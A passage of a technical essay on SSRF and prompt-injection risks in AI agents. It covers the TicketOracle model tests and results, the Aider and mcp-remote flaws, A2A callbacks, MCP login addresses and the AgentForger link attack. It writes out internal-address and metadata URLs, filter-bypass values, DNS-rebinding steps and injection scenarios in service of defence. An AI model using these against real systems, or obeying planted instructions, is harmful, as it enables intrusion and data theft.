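A hand-off can also break a chain. In the earlier test with `ping`, the receiving agent kept only the machine's address. Dropping the rest offers little protection against SSRF, because the address is the payload and the receiving agent needs an address to do its job.

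Splitting work between agents would probably limit what a malicious helper can collect, because the helper can obtain only what the agent calling it knows. An agent that has received only a URL has little else to reveal. Corruption is probably harder to contain, because the next agent receives the changed value and may never learn that a helper changed it.

### Keeping the origin with the value

Wu and colleagues recommend several checks but do not test them. A tool that sends network requests should accept only permitted hosts and URL schemes. Tools should exchange data in structured objects that record which tool produced each value and whether it came from the user or from outside. This extends the idea of the `url_source` field in the supplier example to files and other stores.

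ChainFuzzer also suggests that software should reject a dangerous call when an untrusted value reaches a sensitive argument. Its examples are database queries and page templates, which outsiders have little legitimate reason to write in full. The same rule would be too strict for URLs, as in the supplier example. A system therefore needs different rules for different arguments, and PACT limits tool calls this way at run time.

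These rules depend on keeping a record of each value's origin when the value is stored. Cai and colleagues built NeuroTaint, which saves this record beside the value and restores it when an agent retrieves the value. They tested it on 400 scenarios, half of which contained a flow from an outside source to a sensitive tool. About 92% of the flows it reported were genuine, and it found about 94% of those present. They designed the benchmark around the kinds of flow that NeuroTaint is built to detect, so the tool may do less well on others. NeuroTaint examines logs only after the agent has finished, which helps an investigator but does not stop the request.

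Outside content can also influence a call without supplying any of its arguments. Suppose a web page persuades an agent to send a report to an address that the user had supplied for another purpose. A label recording the address's origin would show that it came from the user, but not that the page influenced the call. ChainFuzzer would miss this influence too, because it looks for values that move between tools. NeuroTaint replaces the page with neutral text and asks a language model to predict whether the agent would still have made the call, but that prediction could be wrong.

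## TicketOracle: an agent sent to an internal address

ChainFuzzer ran 20 applications with one model, whereas *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) tested seven models in one application. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian built TicketOracle, a concert website whose assistant can fetch any URL, and tried to make each model contact an administrative service that outsiders cannot reach. One model contacted the service in every trial of every direct attack, and two never did. No code checked where requests were going, so whether an attack succeeded depended only on the model.

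### The website and its administrative service

TicketOracle runs two services on one machine. The public service holds concert details, ticket prices and visitors' reviews, and runs the chat assistant. The administrative service holds user records and can create or delete users and events. It listens only on `127.0.0.1`, a loopback address that a machine uses to connect to itself, so other machines cannot reach it. It requires no login.

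The assistant has one tool, `fetch_event_data`, which takes a URL, sends a GET request and returns the response, cut to a fixed length. The first call below gets the reviews of a concert and the second gets the user records:

```
fetch_event_data("http://192.168.10.74:5000/events/metallica/reviews")
fetch_event_data("http://127.0.0.1:8000/admin/users")
```

The number after the colon is the port, which determines which program on the machine receives the request. Both calls are valid, and the second works because the tool runs on the same machine as the administrative service. By convention, GET requests only read data, but this service also deletes users in response to them, so a tool limited to GET can still do lasting damage.

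The attacker can chat with the assistant and post reviews but has no credentials. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian assume he can guess administrative paths from common names such as `/admin/users`. In every test the attacker supplied the full URL, so the model never had to work out an internal address.

### Four direct attacks and a planted review

In the four direct attacks, the attacker wrote to the assistant in the chat. The first was a port probe, in which the assistant requested a given port on its own machine and its reply revealed whether a program was listening there. Attackers have also used SSRF to scan ports in practice, as in an April 2026 case listed in GCVE's *CWE 918*, a database entry on this type of flaw. In the second attack, the attacker asked for the user records, and in the third, the attacker asked the assistant to delete a user or an event. The fourth, called blind SSRF,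 also changed data, but the service returned an empty response, so only the server's log showed that the request had arrived.

In the fifth attack, the attacker planted an instruction in a review, which the assistant read while answering another visitor's question about the concert. The published example makes the assistant fetch the user records and include them in its reply. That reply goes to the visitor, not the attacker, so an attacker would probably gain more by planting a request to delete something.

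Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tested two system prompts, which are the instructions a developer gives a model. The open prompt placed no limits on URLs. The hardened prompt listed the permitted URL patterns and concert names and instructed the model to refuse anything else. In April 2026, they ran each attack ten times on each model, and the table shows how many attempts succeeded.

| Model | Port probe | User records | Deletion | Blind request | Planted review, open prompt | Planted review, hardened prompt |
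|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 6 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 | 5 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The direct attacks in the table used the open prompt. With the hardened prompt, all of them failed on every model.

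The deletion request, arguably the most harmful, also succeeded most often. All five models that followed any direct attack carried it out in all ten trials, including Gemini, which refused the port probe and the blind request. Resistance to direct attacks did not predict resistance to a planted one. Qwen and DeepSeek followed nearly every direct attack but never the one planted in the review. GPT-oss never disclosed the user records when asked directly, but it followed the planted attack in half the trials.

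### How much the success rates show

The ten trials of each attack took place in one conversation, and the model received the whole history each time, so its earlier answers could influence later ones. Claude's refusals became shorter as the attacker repeated the same message. In the port probe, they went from long explanations almost to single words. A score of ten or zero may therefore reflect one decision that the model kept repeating. Even if the trials were independent, an attack that works a quarter of the time would fail all ten about 6% of the time.

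The blind request suggests that the results may depend heavily on wording. It changes data just as the deletion does, yet Gemini and GPT-oss went from ten successes on the deletion to none on the blind request. The empty response does not explain why they refused the first time, because it arrives only after a model sends the request. The message or the URL more likely caused the refusals. The scores may therefore reflect the particular messages more than the types of attack.

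The scoring also misses some harmful requests. Except in the blind test, a trial succeeded only if the assistant sent the request and then repeated the resulting data in its answer. If it deleted a user and didn't mention it, the trial counted as a failure. GPT-oss's zero for the user records could mean that it refused to request them, or that it requested them but left the phone numbers out of its answer. Claude's zeros are easier to interpret, because Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian report that it never ran the fetch.

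They also conclude that the hardened prompt made the planted review more effective against Llama, where it succeeded ten times instead of six. But they had added text to the review to get around the hardened prompt's list of permitted URLs, and that text could explain the increase. The increase could also be due to chance, which would produce a difference at least this large about 9% of the time even if the trials were independent.

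Llama's ten failures show that the hardened prompt's protection depends on the model applying the allowlist correctly. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian write that the allowlist catches bad URLs before the model can reason about them, but it was only text in the prompt, so the model had to read it, compare the URL and refuse. The planted review claimed that someone had extended the list, and Llama acted on that claim. A list in the tool's code would have blocked the request regardless of the model's output.

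The perfect scores of GPT-5.2 and Claude are encouraging, but every attack included an instruction to fetch the address, and TicketOracle did not refine its messages to overcome a model's refusals. GPT-5.2 was far weaker against forged data in Choi and colleagues' tests. TicketOracle also did not test an altered link like the supplier's, which contains no instruction. It used only one agent, so it does not show what a fetching agent would do with an address from a cooperating agent.

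### A destination check in code

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian consider checks in the application's code the most important defence, because these do not depend on the model's compliance. They recommend such checks but do not test them. TicketOracle could use a simple one in which the model supplies only a concert's identifier, such as `metallica`, and the code builds the URL, so the model cannot choose a different host.

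An agent that reads the open web needs a more general check, because its developer can't list every useful page in advance. The check belongs in the tool that sends the request, and it has seven steps:

1. Parse the URL once, and refuse it if it contains a backslash or a user name.
2. Refuse every scheme except `https`, or `http` where the task needs it, and every port except the usual one for that scheme.
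3. If there is an allowlist of hosts, refuse any host that is not on it.
4. Look up the host's name and collect all the network addresses it leads to.
5. Refuse the request if any of them is a loopback, private, link-local or otherwise reserved address.
6. Connect to one of the addresses just checked, without looking up the name again.
7. If the response is a redirect, start again at step 1 with the new URL, and stop after a few redirects.

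The second step excludes URLs such as `file:///etc/passwd`, which some programs read from the local disk without using the network. *SSRF Protection*, in the documentation for the PHP web framework Nette, describes a ready-made check with similar defaults, accepting only `https` on port 443 and public addresses. Developers do not always have a ready-made check available. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian found that Guardrails AI, a library of checks for language-model applications, had one for database queries but none that directly fitted most of their other attacks.

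The fifth step covers three main groups of addresses, which in the older and still common IPv4 format are these:

| Type | IPv4 addresses | What an attacker might reach |
|---|---|---|
| Loopback | `127.0.0.0` to `127.255.255.255` | Services on the same machine, such as TicketOracle's administrative service |
| Private | Those beginning `10.` or `192.168.`, and `172.16.0.0` to `172.31.255.255` | Other machines in the organisation, such as the payroll server |
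| Link-local | Those beginning `169.254.` | Services attached to the machine's own network link, including cloud metadata |

A cloud metadata service gives a virtual machine information about itself, often including temporary credentials for the owner's cloud account. It is usually at `169.254.169.254`. The check has to cover both IPv4 and IPv6, because IPv6 has its own versions of all three groups and an IPv6 address can contain an IPv4 address.

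OWASP's *A10:2021* (2021) advises against deny lists, which name forbidden destinations, because attackers have tools for getting around them. It recommends allowlists for the scheme, port and destination instead. The fifth step checks the numerical address after the lookup and refuses every reserved range. This resembles a deny list but amounts to allowing only public addresses, which is still weaker than an allowlist of hosts. OWASP's 2021 list of the ten main web risks gave SSRF its own entry. SecurityWeek's *Two New Web Application Risk Categories Added to OWASP Top 10* (2025) reports that a near-final draft of the 2025 list moved it under broken access control.

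Include Security's *Mitigating SSRF in 2023* (2023) gives an example of a deny list that fails. The code extracts the host from the URL and compares it with four entries, `127.0.0.1`, `localhost`, `169.254.169.254` and `0.0.0.0`. The payroll server's address, `10.0.4.17`, is not on the list and would pass. So would `127.0.0.2`, which is also a loopback address, and `2130706433`, which many programs treat as `127.0.0.1`.

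### When two programs read a URL differently

Even a good list fails if the check and the request disagree about which host the URL names. Consider this one:

`http://10.0.4.17\@supplier.example/prices`

The URL standard allows a user name before the host, separated from it by `@`. Python's common `urlparse` function follows this rule loosely, treating everything before the `@` as a user name and returning `supplier.example` as the host. Web browsers treat a backslash as a forward slash, so they take `10.0.4.17` as the host and the rest as the path. If an agent's developer checks URLs with `urlparse` and fetches pages with a browser, the URL passes the check as the supplier's, but the browser contacts the payroll server.

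Unicode conversions can cause the same problem, and OWASP (2024) advises developers to watch for them when validating input. Some software converts the wide digits used in East Asian text into ordinary ones, so a host that did not look like a numerical address during the check may become one before the request.

Parsing the URL once removes the disagreement between parsers only if the request uses the parsed result. The check should pass the host, port and path it found to the code that makes the connection, or build a new URL from them. If it passes on the original text instead, a second parser may still read the URL differently. Refusing URLs that contain backslashes or user names should block few ordinary public links, since they rarely need either.

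### DNS rebinding

Machines connect to numerical addresses, so a program must first look up the host's name in the domain name system (DNS). The owner of the name controls which address the lookup returns. *Preventing Server Side Request Forgery in Golang*, a guide for programmers, explains that an attacker can point a public name at an internal address. Nothing in `http://prices.attacker.example/october.csv` looks internal, so a check can find the problem only by looking up the name.

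Looking it up once in the check and again for the request creates another opening. In DNS rebinding, the attacker changes the answer between the two lookups:

1. The check looks up `prices.attacker.example`, and the attacker's DNS server returns a public address, with an instruction not to keep the answer for long.
2. The check finds nothing wrong and approves the URL.
3. The program that sends the request looks up the name again, and the attacker's server now returns `10.0.4.17`.
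4. The request goes to the payroll server.

OWASP groups DNS rebinding with "time of check, time of use" flaws, in which something changes between a check and the action it was meant to protect. The gap here may be milliseconds, but it can be days if a system stores an address for later use, as some agent protocols do with callback addresses.

The remedy is to connect to the address that passed the check. *CWE 918*, a guide for developers, also accepts a second check when the program connects, and it calls for testing every address that the lookup returns. If a name leads to one public and one private address and the program checks only the public one, it may connect to the private one. The request must still carry the original name, because one machine often hosts many websites and the program needs the name to verify the site's certificate. If requests go out through a proxy, the proxy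 usually does the lookup, so it must also check the addresses.

Requiring `https` adds some protection, because the program would send the payroll server a request only if the server had a valid certificate for the attacker's hostname. The program would still try to connect, though, and OWASP notes that the result or duration of a connection attempt can reveal which ports are open.

### Redirects and pages that load other pages

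A web server can answer a request with a redirect, a response whose `Location` header gives another URL. Most programs follow redirects automatically, so the attacker can supply a public URL that passes the check and have its server redirect the agent to `http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export`. GCVE lists a 2024 flaw of this kind in a framework for building language-model applications. The framework's tool for retrieving web pages would follow a crafted `Location` header to local addresses.

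OWASP recommends turning redirects off. This is the safest choice for a tool that fetches from a few known addresses, but websites use redirects when pages move, so an agent that reads the open web would lose many legitimate pages. The agent can still reach them if it turns off only automatic redirect following and runs the full check on each new URL before fetching it.

Agents that open pages in a full browser are harder to protect, because the browser also loads images, scripts and embedded pages, any of which may come from a different host. Secure Code Warrior, a company that trains developers, recommends a simple HTTP client where it is sufficient, because a browser gives attackers more to exploit. If the task needs a browser, the check has to apply to each connection the browser makes, for instance in a proxy that handles all its traffic.

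### Aider: a confirmed request to cloud metadata

A user's approval is no substitute for any of these steps, as an SSRF flaw in the coding agent Aider shows. *AGENTLENS* (Lv, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a program that maps an agent's components, looks for routes from outside input to dangerous operations, and tests those routes in multi-turn conversations. It found 44 vulnerabilities in five coding agents. Twelve, including the one in Aider, have since received CVE numbers, the standard identifiers for publicly known software flaws.

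The attacker controls a README that lists the address of a cloud metadata service as the location of internal documentation. The developer asks Aider to read the project's configuration, then to write a function that downloads the documentation and to fetch the address as a test. Aider extracts the URL from the developer's request and asks for confirmation. Once the developer agrees, Aider's page-fetching function requests the URL without checking whether the address is internal.

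The confirmation shows that the developer wants Aider to fetch the documentation, but not that the address leads to documentation. Some developers will recognise `169.254.169.254`, but others will see an address that matches the project's instructions. A rule that allows only addresses the user wrote would not have helped either, because by then the developer had asked for this one. The fifth step of the destination check would have stopped the fetch.

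The evidence shows that Aider sent the requests, but it doesn't show that anyone stole credentials. Lv and colleagues' entry for the flaw describes "request attempts", and on an ordinary laptop usually nothing responds at that address. The danger is greater when Aider runs on a cloud machine whose metadata service gives out credentials without further checks. Even then, the response goes to Aider, so the attacker needs another step to obtain it. The attacker also needs the developer to ask for the URL, which makes this harder to exploit than a planted review that another visitor's question triggers.

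In the rest of the test, Aider wrote the download function without a destination check and saved it in the project. It then wrote a test script to call the function with the same metadata address, and Lv and colleagues asked it to run the script. Requests from code that an agent writes do not pass through its page-fetching tool, so a check inside that tool would not stop the script's request or protect anyone who later used the function in another program.

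Network rules can cover such code. OWASP recommends that firewalls block internal traffic by default and allow only what is essential. However, a firewall between machines could not block a TicketOracle request to `127.0.0.1`, because the request does not leave the machine. Moving the agent to another machine, or into a container with its own loopback address, would prevent it from reaching the administrative service directly. Requiring a login for that service would help even if a request reached it.

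Another of the Aider flaws arose when one model handed work to another. Aider can split a task between an architect model, which plans changes, and an editor model, which writes them. When Aider starts the editor, it turns off a step that would otherwise validate the architect's output, so instructions in a README could influence the code that the editor writes. Similarly, a destination check that ran only while Aider processed its input would miss a URL that one agent passed to another by a route that skipped this processing. It is safer to check the destination in the tool that sends the request.

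### The supplier's link after the full check

Suppose the company adds the seven steps to its fetching agent, without an allowlist of hosts, and permits only `https`. An attacker who controls the supplier's page can try several links:

| Link on the supplier's page | Result |
|---|---|
| `https://supplier.example/prices/october.csv`, the real price list | Allowed |
| `http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export` | Refused for its scheme, and its private address would fail too |
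| `https://prices.attacker.example/october.csv`, a name that leads to `10.0.4.17` | Refused after the lookup |
| `https://attacker.example/october.csv`, which redirects to the payroll server | Refused at the redirect |
| `https://attacker.example/october.csv`, which returns a false price list | Allowed |
| `https://supplier.example/orders/cancel?id=311` | Allowed |

The false price list comes from a public machine, so the check does not block it. The company may order parts at the wrong price, and the file may also contain instructions for the planning agent. Some software relies even more heavily on what it downloads. *API 07:2023 — Server Side Request Forgery* (2023) mentions attacks on login tokens in which a server loads a resource from the attacker's machine. If that resource is the key used to verify tokens, the server will accept tokens that the attacker has signed.

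An allowlist containing only `supplier.example` would stop the false price list, as long as the attacker couldn't put the file on the supplier's own site. It would not stop the cancellation link, because that link points to the permitted host. Fetching the link would cancel an order if the supplier's site accepts cancellations through GET requests and the agent is logged in to the company's account. The site might also trust any request from the company's network, and then the agent would not need to log in. The allowlist also doesn't prevent an agent from sending private data to a permitted host inside the URL.

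Refusing all private addresses would also block this agent's normal work, because the company placed it inside the network to fetch internal documents. TicketOracle's public service is also at a private address, `192.168.10.74`, so the fifth step would block its ordinary concert lookups as well as the attacks. An exception for the document server would let the company's agent work normally, but the altered link could then point to a confidential document on that server.

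The company could get around this by applying OWASP's recommendation to keep remote fetching in a separate network. One tool would fetch public pages from a network without access to internal machines. A second tool would fetch internal documents and accept only document numbers, not web addresses. This would keep the altered link away from the payroll server. However, a supplier's page could still contain a valid document number, so the second tool would also need an origin check.

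## A2A and MCP: addresses inside agent protocols

The three agents in the supplier example can exchange addresses in whatever format their developers choose, but agents and tools from different companies need a shared one. Agent2Agent (A2A) is an open standard for connecting agents to each other, and the Model Context Protocol (MCP) is one for connecting agents to tools and data. Both have fields in which one party gives another an address that the recipient's software will contact. Ordinary code often contacts the address without a model reading it, so an attacker can misuse the field without prompt injection.

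### The address fields

In A2A, the agent that requests work is the client and the agent that does it is the remote agent. Under version 1.0 of the *Agent2Agent (A2A) Protocol Specification*, each remote agent publishes an agent card, a file that lists its skills, its login requirements and the address where it receives requests. Messages and results consist of parts, and a part can contain the URL of a file. For long tasks, the client can also register a callback, an address to which the remote agent posts updates.

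In MCP, the client is the part of an agent's program that connects to an MCP server, which offers the tools. A server that restricts access can use OAuth, a standard for giving a program a token that lets it act for a user. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026) describes how the client follows a series of addresses to find the authorization server, which issues the tokens.

| Protocol and field | Who supplies the address | Who contacts it, and why |
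|---|---|---|
| A2A: `url` under `supportedInterfaces` in the agent card | Remote agent | Client, to send tasks |
| A2A: `tokenUrl`, `openIdConnectUrl` and similar fields in the card | Remote agent | Client, to log in |
| A2A: `url` in a message part | Either agent | The receiving agent, to get a file |
| A2A: `url` in the callback settings | Client | Remote agent, to post updates |
| MCP: `resource_metadata` | MCP server | Client, to learn how to log in |
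| MCP: `authorization_servers` | MCP server | Client, to find the authorization server |
| MCP: `authorization_endpoint` | Authorization server | The user's browser, to ask for approval |
| MCP: `token_endpoint` | Authorization server | Client, to get a token |
| MCP: `client_id`, when it is a URL | Client | Authorization server, to read about the client |

The address in an agent card can be on a different host from the one that published the card. A2A requires the address to use `https` in production, but an `https` address can still point to an internal machine.

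MCP servers can also supply links while a client is using their tools. *MCP-38* (2026), a classification of threats to MCP, warns that a client that fetches these links without enough validation may contact internal services.

### A callback to the wrong machine

Suppose the supplier runs an A2A agent that prepares quotes, which takes several hours. The company's planning agent is the client. It checks the quote agent's card to confirm that it supports callbacks, then sends this request:

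```
{ "message": {
    "messageId": "m-41",
    "role": "ROLE_USER",
    "parts": [ { "text": "Quote for 400 brake cables" } ] },
  "configuration": {
    "returnImmediately": true,
    "taskPushNotificationConfig": {
      "url": "https://buyer.example/a2a/quotes",
      "authentication": { "scheme": "Bearer",
                          "credentials": "(secret for this task)" } } } }
```

The rest takes four steps:

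1. The quote agent creates a task, gives it an identifier and returns this to the planning agent at once.
2. It stores the callback settings while it works.
3. When it finishes, its software sends a POST request to the callback address, with the secret in the `Authorization` header and the task in the body.
4. The company's server checks the secret and the task identifier, then confirms receipt.

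An attacker could open a customer account with the supplier and request a quote with `http://10.0.8.5/stock/reset` as the callback. That address belongs to a machine on the supplier's network that the quote agent can reach but the attacker cannot. When the quote is ready, the agent posts it to that address. If the machine resets the stock records whenever it receives a POST request at that path, the attack succeeds.

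The quote agent is a confused deputy, much like Hardy's compiler, which wrote its output to whatever file the user named. A better model would not fix this, because the model does not need to read the address.

The attacker may never see the internal machine's response, because it goes to the quote agent, and many services would reject the request's body, which has a fixed A2A format. But the attacker also chooses the credentials in the `Authorization` header, so the request might work on a service that still accepts a factory-set password. The quote agent may also send several requests, because A2A allows it to post an update whenever the task's state changes and to retry failed deliveries. *Streaming and Asynchronous Operations for Long-Running Tasks*, a guide to A2A, warns that attackers could use callbacks to flood an unrelated website with traffic.

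A false callback address can also send data to the wrong party. Suppose the planning agent reads its callback address from a shared settings file, and an attacker replaces it with the address of his own server. The quote agent then sends him the company's quote and the secret for that callback, which he could use to send the company a forged quote. A2A recommends a separate secret for each callback, which would limit the forgery to this task.

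The address in that second attack is public and can use `https`, so a check for internal machines would not stop it. A2A requires the remote agent to verify that a client has the right to set callbacks for a task, which should prevent one customer from redirecting another's results. That check would not stop this attack either, because the planning agent has the right to set callbacks for its own task.

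### Mandatory and recommended checks on callbacks

The A2A specification marks some checks as mandatory ("MUST") and others as recommended ("SHOULD").

| Check | Who performs it | Status in A2A |
|---|---|---|
| Refuse private, loopback and link-local addresses | Remote agent | Recommended |
| Accept only addresses on an allowlist | Remote agent | Recommended where appropriate |
| Send the agreed credentials with each notification | Remote agent | Mandatory |
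| Verify those credentials | Client | Mandatory in the security rules, recommended in looser terms elsewhere |
| Match the task identifier to an expected task | Client | Mandatory in the description of notifications, recommended in the security rules |
| Prove that the client controls the callback address | Both | Not in the callback rules; the guide suggests it |
| Sign notifications | Remote agent | Not in the callback rules |

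The strictest callback requirements protect the client from forged notifications. The checks that would stop the quote agent from posting to its own network are only recommended, so an agent can follow every mandatory callback rule and still have this flaw. The specification does require software to validate file references against SSRF, in its registration of A2A's media type, but it does not explain how.

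Some organisations legitimately run their agents on local addresses, which is a reason not to ban private addresses outright. *Prepare URL validation infrastructure for agent card and webhook SSRF protection* (ishymko), a task description for A2A's Python software, therefore describes a planned check that is adjustable. The check would cover both agent cards and callbacks, and the software would connect to the numerical address it had just checked, as in the full destination check described for TicketOracle.

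An allowlist should be specific to each client. If the supplier keeps one list of all its customers' hosts, an attacker with a customer account can get their own host onto it and redirect another company's quotes there. A separate list for the planning agent, agreed when the company opened its account, would contain only `buyer.example` and block both the internal address and the attacker's server.

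The guide to A2A also suggests making the client prove that it owns the address. In a typical challenge, the remote agent sends a random value to the callback and activates the callback only if the server there returns the value. Unrelated websites and most internal services would fail this test. But the challenge is itself a request to an unverified address, so the remote agent should check the destination first. A simple challenge also won't stop an attacker who supplies his own server, since that server will return the value. Stopping him would require a response that includes something only the client can produce, such as a signature made with its private key.

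A signature over the whole notification lets the client check that the remote agent wrote this particular result and that nobody changed it. A shared secret shows only that the sender knows the secret, so anyone who obtains it can write a notification. Signing does not prevent the remote agent from sending the result to the wrong place.

### Following addresses to log in to an MCP server

In MCP, a false address mainly endangers the client. The client sends a request without a token, and the MCP server refuses with a response that includes a `resource_metadata` address. The client fetches the document at that address, which lists one or more authorization servers. It then chooses one and fetches that server's description, which contains the addresses for user approval and for tokens. A malicious MCP server can choose the first address and, through it, all the others.

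The Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices* describes an attack in which a malicious server gives the address of a cloud metadata service as `resource_metadata`, and the client fetches it from inside its own network. Part of the response may then reach the attacker through an error message. The token address is more dangerous in one respect, because the client sends a POST request there, which could change data on an internal service.

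Under this guidance, a client that runs on a server must consider SSRF and implement appropriate protections, though the specific protections are only recommended. These recommendations largely match the TicketOracle check, but the guidance warns developers against writing their own code to recognise private addresses, because such code often misses unusual encodings.

MCP encourages clients to identify themselves to the authorization server with a URL, which the server fetches to read the client's name and permitted callback addresses. A malicious client could therefore try server-side request forgery (SSRF) on the authorization server as well. Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations* (2026) recommends that authorization servers consider this risk.

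When a client uses several authorization servers, an attacker who controls one of them may try to make the client send him a login code from an honest one. The July 2026 revision of MCP also added a check against this. Before the user logs in, the client must record the authorization server's identity, called the issuer. If the response names an issuer, the client must compare the two and reject a mismatch. Model Context Protocol warns that this gives no protection if the expected issuer came from an unvalidated source. If a malicious server led the client to the attacker's authorization server, the recorded and returned issuers will match.

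MCP also limits where a token works. When the client requests a token, it must name the MCP server it will use the token with, and each MCP server must reject tokens that were not issued for it. So if a false address leads the client to log in to a malicious server, that server should not be able to use the resulting token elsewhere. The rule does not stop the client from contacting an internal address during login, because the client does not have a token yet.

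### CVE-2025-6514: a login address that ran commands

The program mcp-remote lets desktop applications that support only local MCP servers connect to remote ones. In *Critical RCE Vulnerability in mcp-remote* (2025), the software security company JFrog disclosed that a malicious server could use an address it supplied to the program to run commands on the user's computer. The flaw, CVE-2025-6514, affects versions 0.0.5 to 0.1.15. The project's maintainer fixed it in version 0.1.16.

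A user sets up mcp-remote by putting the MCP server's address in a settings file. If the server requires a login, mcp-remote fetches the login addresses from the server and opens one of them, the `authorization_endpoint`, in the user's browser. The vulnerable versions opened it with a library that, on Windows, inserted the address into a PowerShell command. An attacker could write an address that made PowerShell run the attacker's command as well.

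On Windows, JFrog gained full control over the command. On macOS and Linux, an attacker could start programs but had limited control over what they did. If the user connected over unencrypted `http`, an attacker on the same local network could insert the address by changing the server's response, without running the server.

This was command injection rather than SSRF. The harm came from how the software opened the address, so a check for private network addresses would have missed it. Opening the browser without passing the address through a shell is a more reliable fix than allowing only `https`. An `https`-only rule would have blocked the version of the attack that gave JFrog full control, but JFrog also started a program with an `http` address, and the same method might have worked with `https`.

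JFrog demonstrated the flaw on its own test machine and reported no victims. The user chose only to connect to one server, but that server could then supply a second address the user had never approved. JFrog's advice to connect only to trusted servers over `https` lowers the risk, but an attacker may later take over a trusted server.

### How common SSRF is in MCP servers

*MCP-38* repeats an industry estimate that up to 30% of tested MCP servers are vulnerable to SSRF. The classification did not measure this itself, and the figure is an upper limit, not an average. Academic studies have examined many MCP servers, but their headline counts include all kinds of flaws, not just SSRF.

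- *Exposed by Design* (2026) describes tests of 414 MCP servers that anyone could reach over the internet. They covered ten categories of weakness and led to 68 registered vulnerabilities.
- *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (2026) started from 119 public vulnerability records and confirmed that 24 concerned MCP. Most were command injection, unauthorised access to files through manipulated paths, or other ways to run code.
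- *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions* (2026) assembled 53 vulnerabilities in 45 servers.

None of these totals gives the share of MCP servers with an SSRF flaw. Dividing 68 by 414 would mix SSRF with every other category, and one server may account for several vulnerabilities. The other two collections start from known flaws, so they can show which types people report but not how many servers are safe. These sources therefore provide no good independent support for the 30% figure, and the true rate could be higher or lower.

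Counts of vulnerable servers would also leave out flaws in clients, which follow most of the login-related URLs. The Vulners vulnerability database entry *Spring AI MCP Security* describes a security framework that fetched such URLs without checking whether they led to internal machines.

### What authentication proves

Suppose the company's own agents use A2A, and the attacker has again changed the supplier's link. The planning agent sends this message to the fetching agent:

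```
{ "messageId": "m-52",
  "role": "ROLE_USER",
  "parts": [
    { "text": "Download the current price list" },
    { "url": "http://10.0.4.17/payroll/export" } ] }
```

As in the original supplier example, authentication confirms that the planning agent sent the message but not who chose the address. The `ROLE_USER` label can mislead a developer, because it means only that the message went from client to remote agent, not that the employee wrote it.

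A signature over the message would not help, because the attacker changed the address before the planning agent signed anything. Signed agent cards have the same limit. A2A lets remote agents sign their cards and recommends that clients verify the signatures. Verification reveals whether someone altered a card after signing, but a malicious operator can still sign a card that contains an internal address.

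The supplier still needs authentication to keep a separate allowlist for each customer and to find out which account registered a harmful callback. That account belongs to the attacker if the customer made up the address, but to a company the attacker deceived if an honest planning agent copied the address from an altered file.

The same applies to replies. When the company's server verifies a notification, it confirms that the sender had the right secret. The quote inside may still contain a file URL that the quote agent copied from a third party, so the company's agents should check that URL before they fetch it. *The A2A protocol in 5 bullet points*, by the agent software vendor Archestra, recommends treating even calls from agents in the same organisation as untrusted input, because the calling agent may have just read something malicious.

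The planning agent's software could put an origin record, like the `url_source` field suggested for the supplier example, in the optional `metadata` field of an A2A message part. No standard message field records origin, so the two agents' developers would have to agree on a format, perhaps through an A2A extension. The fetching agent would then have an authenticated statement from the planning agent about where the address came from, but the statement would be only as reliable as the software that recorded it.

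## AgentForger: a link whose parameters created an agent

The address fields in A2A and MCP tell software where to send a request. In July 2026 Zenity, which sells security software for AI agents, disclosed a flaw it named AgentForger, in which the harm came from a link's query parameters rather than its address. The link went to OpenAI's own website, and its parameters contained instructions for an agent that builds other agents. When an employee opened the link, the page submitted the instructions automatically, and the builder created a second agent that took orders from the attacker by email.

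### The link and the builder

OpenAI's Workspace Agents let employees create agents for repeated tasks. An employee describes the task in a chat, and a builder agent sets up the new agent. According to OpenAI's *ChatGPT Workspace Agents for Enterprise and Business*, the employee normally reviews a draft plan before the builder starts and can test the new agent before creating it. The new agent reaches services such as Outlook, Slack and Google Drive through connectors, which the employee authorises.

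Zenity Labs' *AgentForger Part 1* describes two parameters that the builder's page accepted in its URL. One selected a template and the other contained the first prompt. With an invented host and invented parameter names, such a link looks like this:

`https://builder.example/new?template=assistant&first_prompt=(instructions)`

OpenAI's page sent that text as soon as the page loaded. It could reasonably have put the text in the prompt box and waited for the user to send it.

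The attack worked only if the victim clicked the link while logged in to ChatGPT, had access to Workspace Agents and had already authorised at least one connector. Many ChatGPT customers would not have met these conditions. Workspace Agents were off by default for Enterprise customers at launch, and administrators can decide who may build agents.

In Zenity's test, the builder then took these steps without further input from the victim:

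1. It created an agent from the template and wrote its standing instructions.
2. It attached the victim's existing connectors, so no new consent screen appeared.
3. It changed the approval setting for Outlook from "Always ask", the default for actions such as sending email, to "Never ask".
4. It published the agent and scheduled it to run every five minutes.
5. It ran the agent at once in preview mode, which acted on the victim's real accounts.

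The Decoder's *One tampered ChatGPT link could spawn a rogue AI agent* explains that the builder combined twelve hourly schedules to get the five-minute interval.

### Orders by email

On each run, the new agent looked in the victim's mailbox for messages from the attacker's address with a subject beginning "TASK". It carried out the instructions in each message through the connected services and emailed the results back. The victim did not have to keep ChatGPT open.

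In Zenity Labs' *AgentForger Part 2*, the agent given these orders mapped the organisation's staff and projects, and found an employee list with pay data and a presentation about planned job cuts. It also sent colleagues a Teams message, in the victim's name, with a link to a fake login page. Zenity presented its request for passwords from Slack as a graded exercise in preventing data loss. That wording may have helped avoid a refusal, but Zenity reports no comparison with a plain request.

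These orders arrived in retrieved email, as in indirect prompt injection, but the agent had standing instructions to obey them. The attacker's text entered as a URL parameter, reached the builder as if the user had typed it, and shaped the instructions the builder wrote for the new agent, gaining authority at each step. A model trained to ignore commands in email might still have followed these, because its standing instructions named the attacker's address as the source of its tasks.

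### The report and the fix

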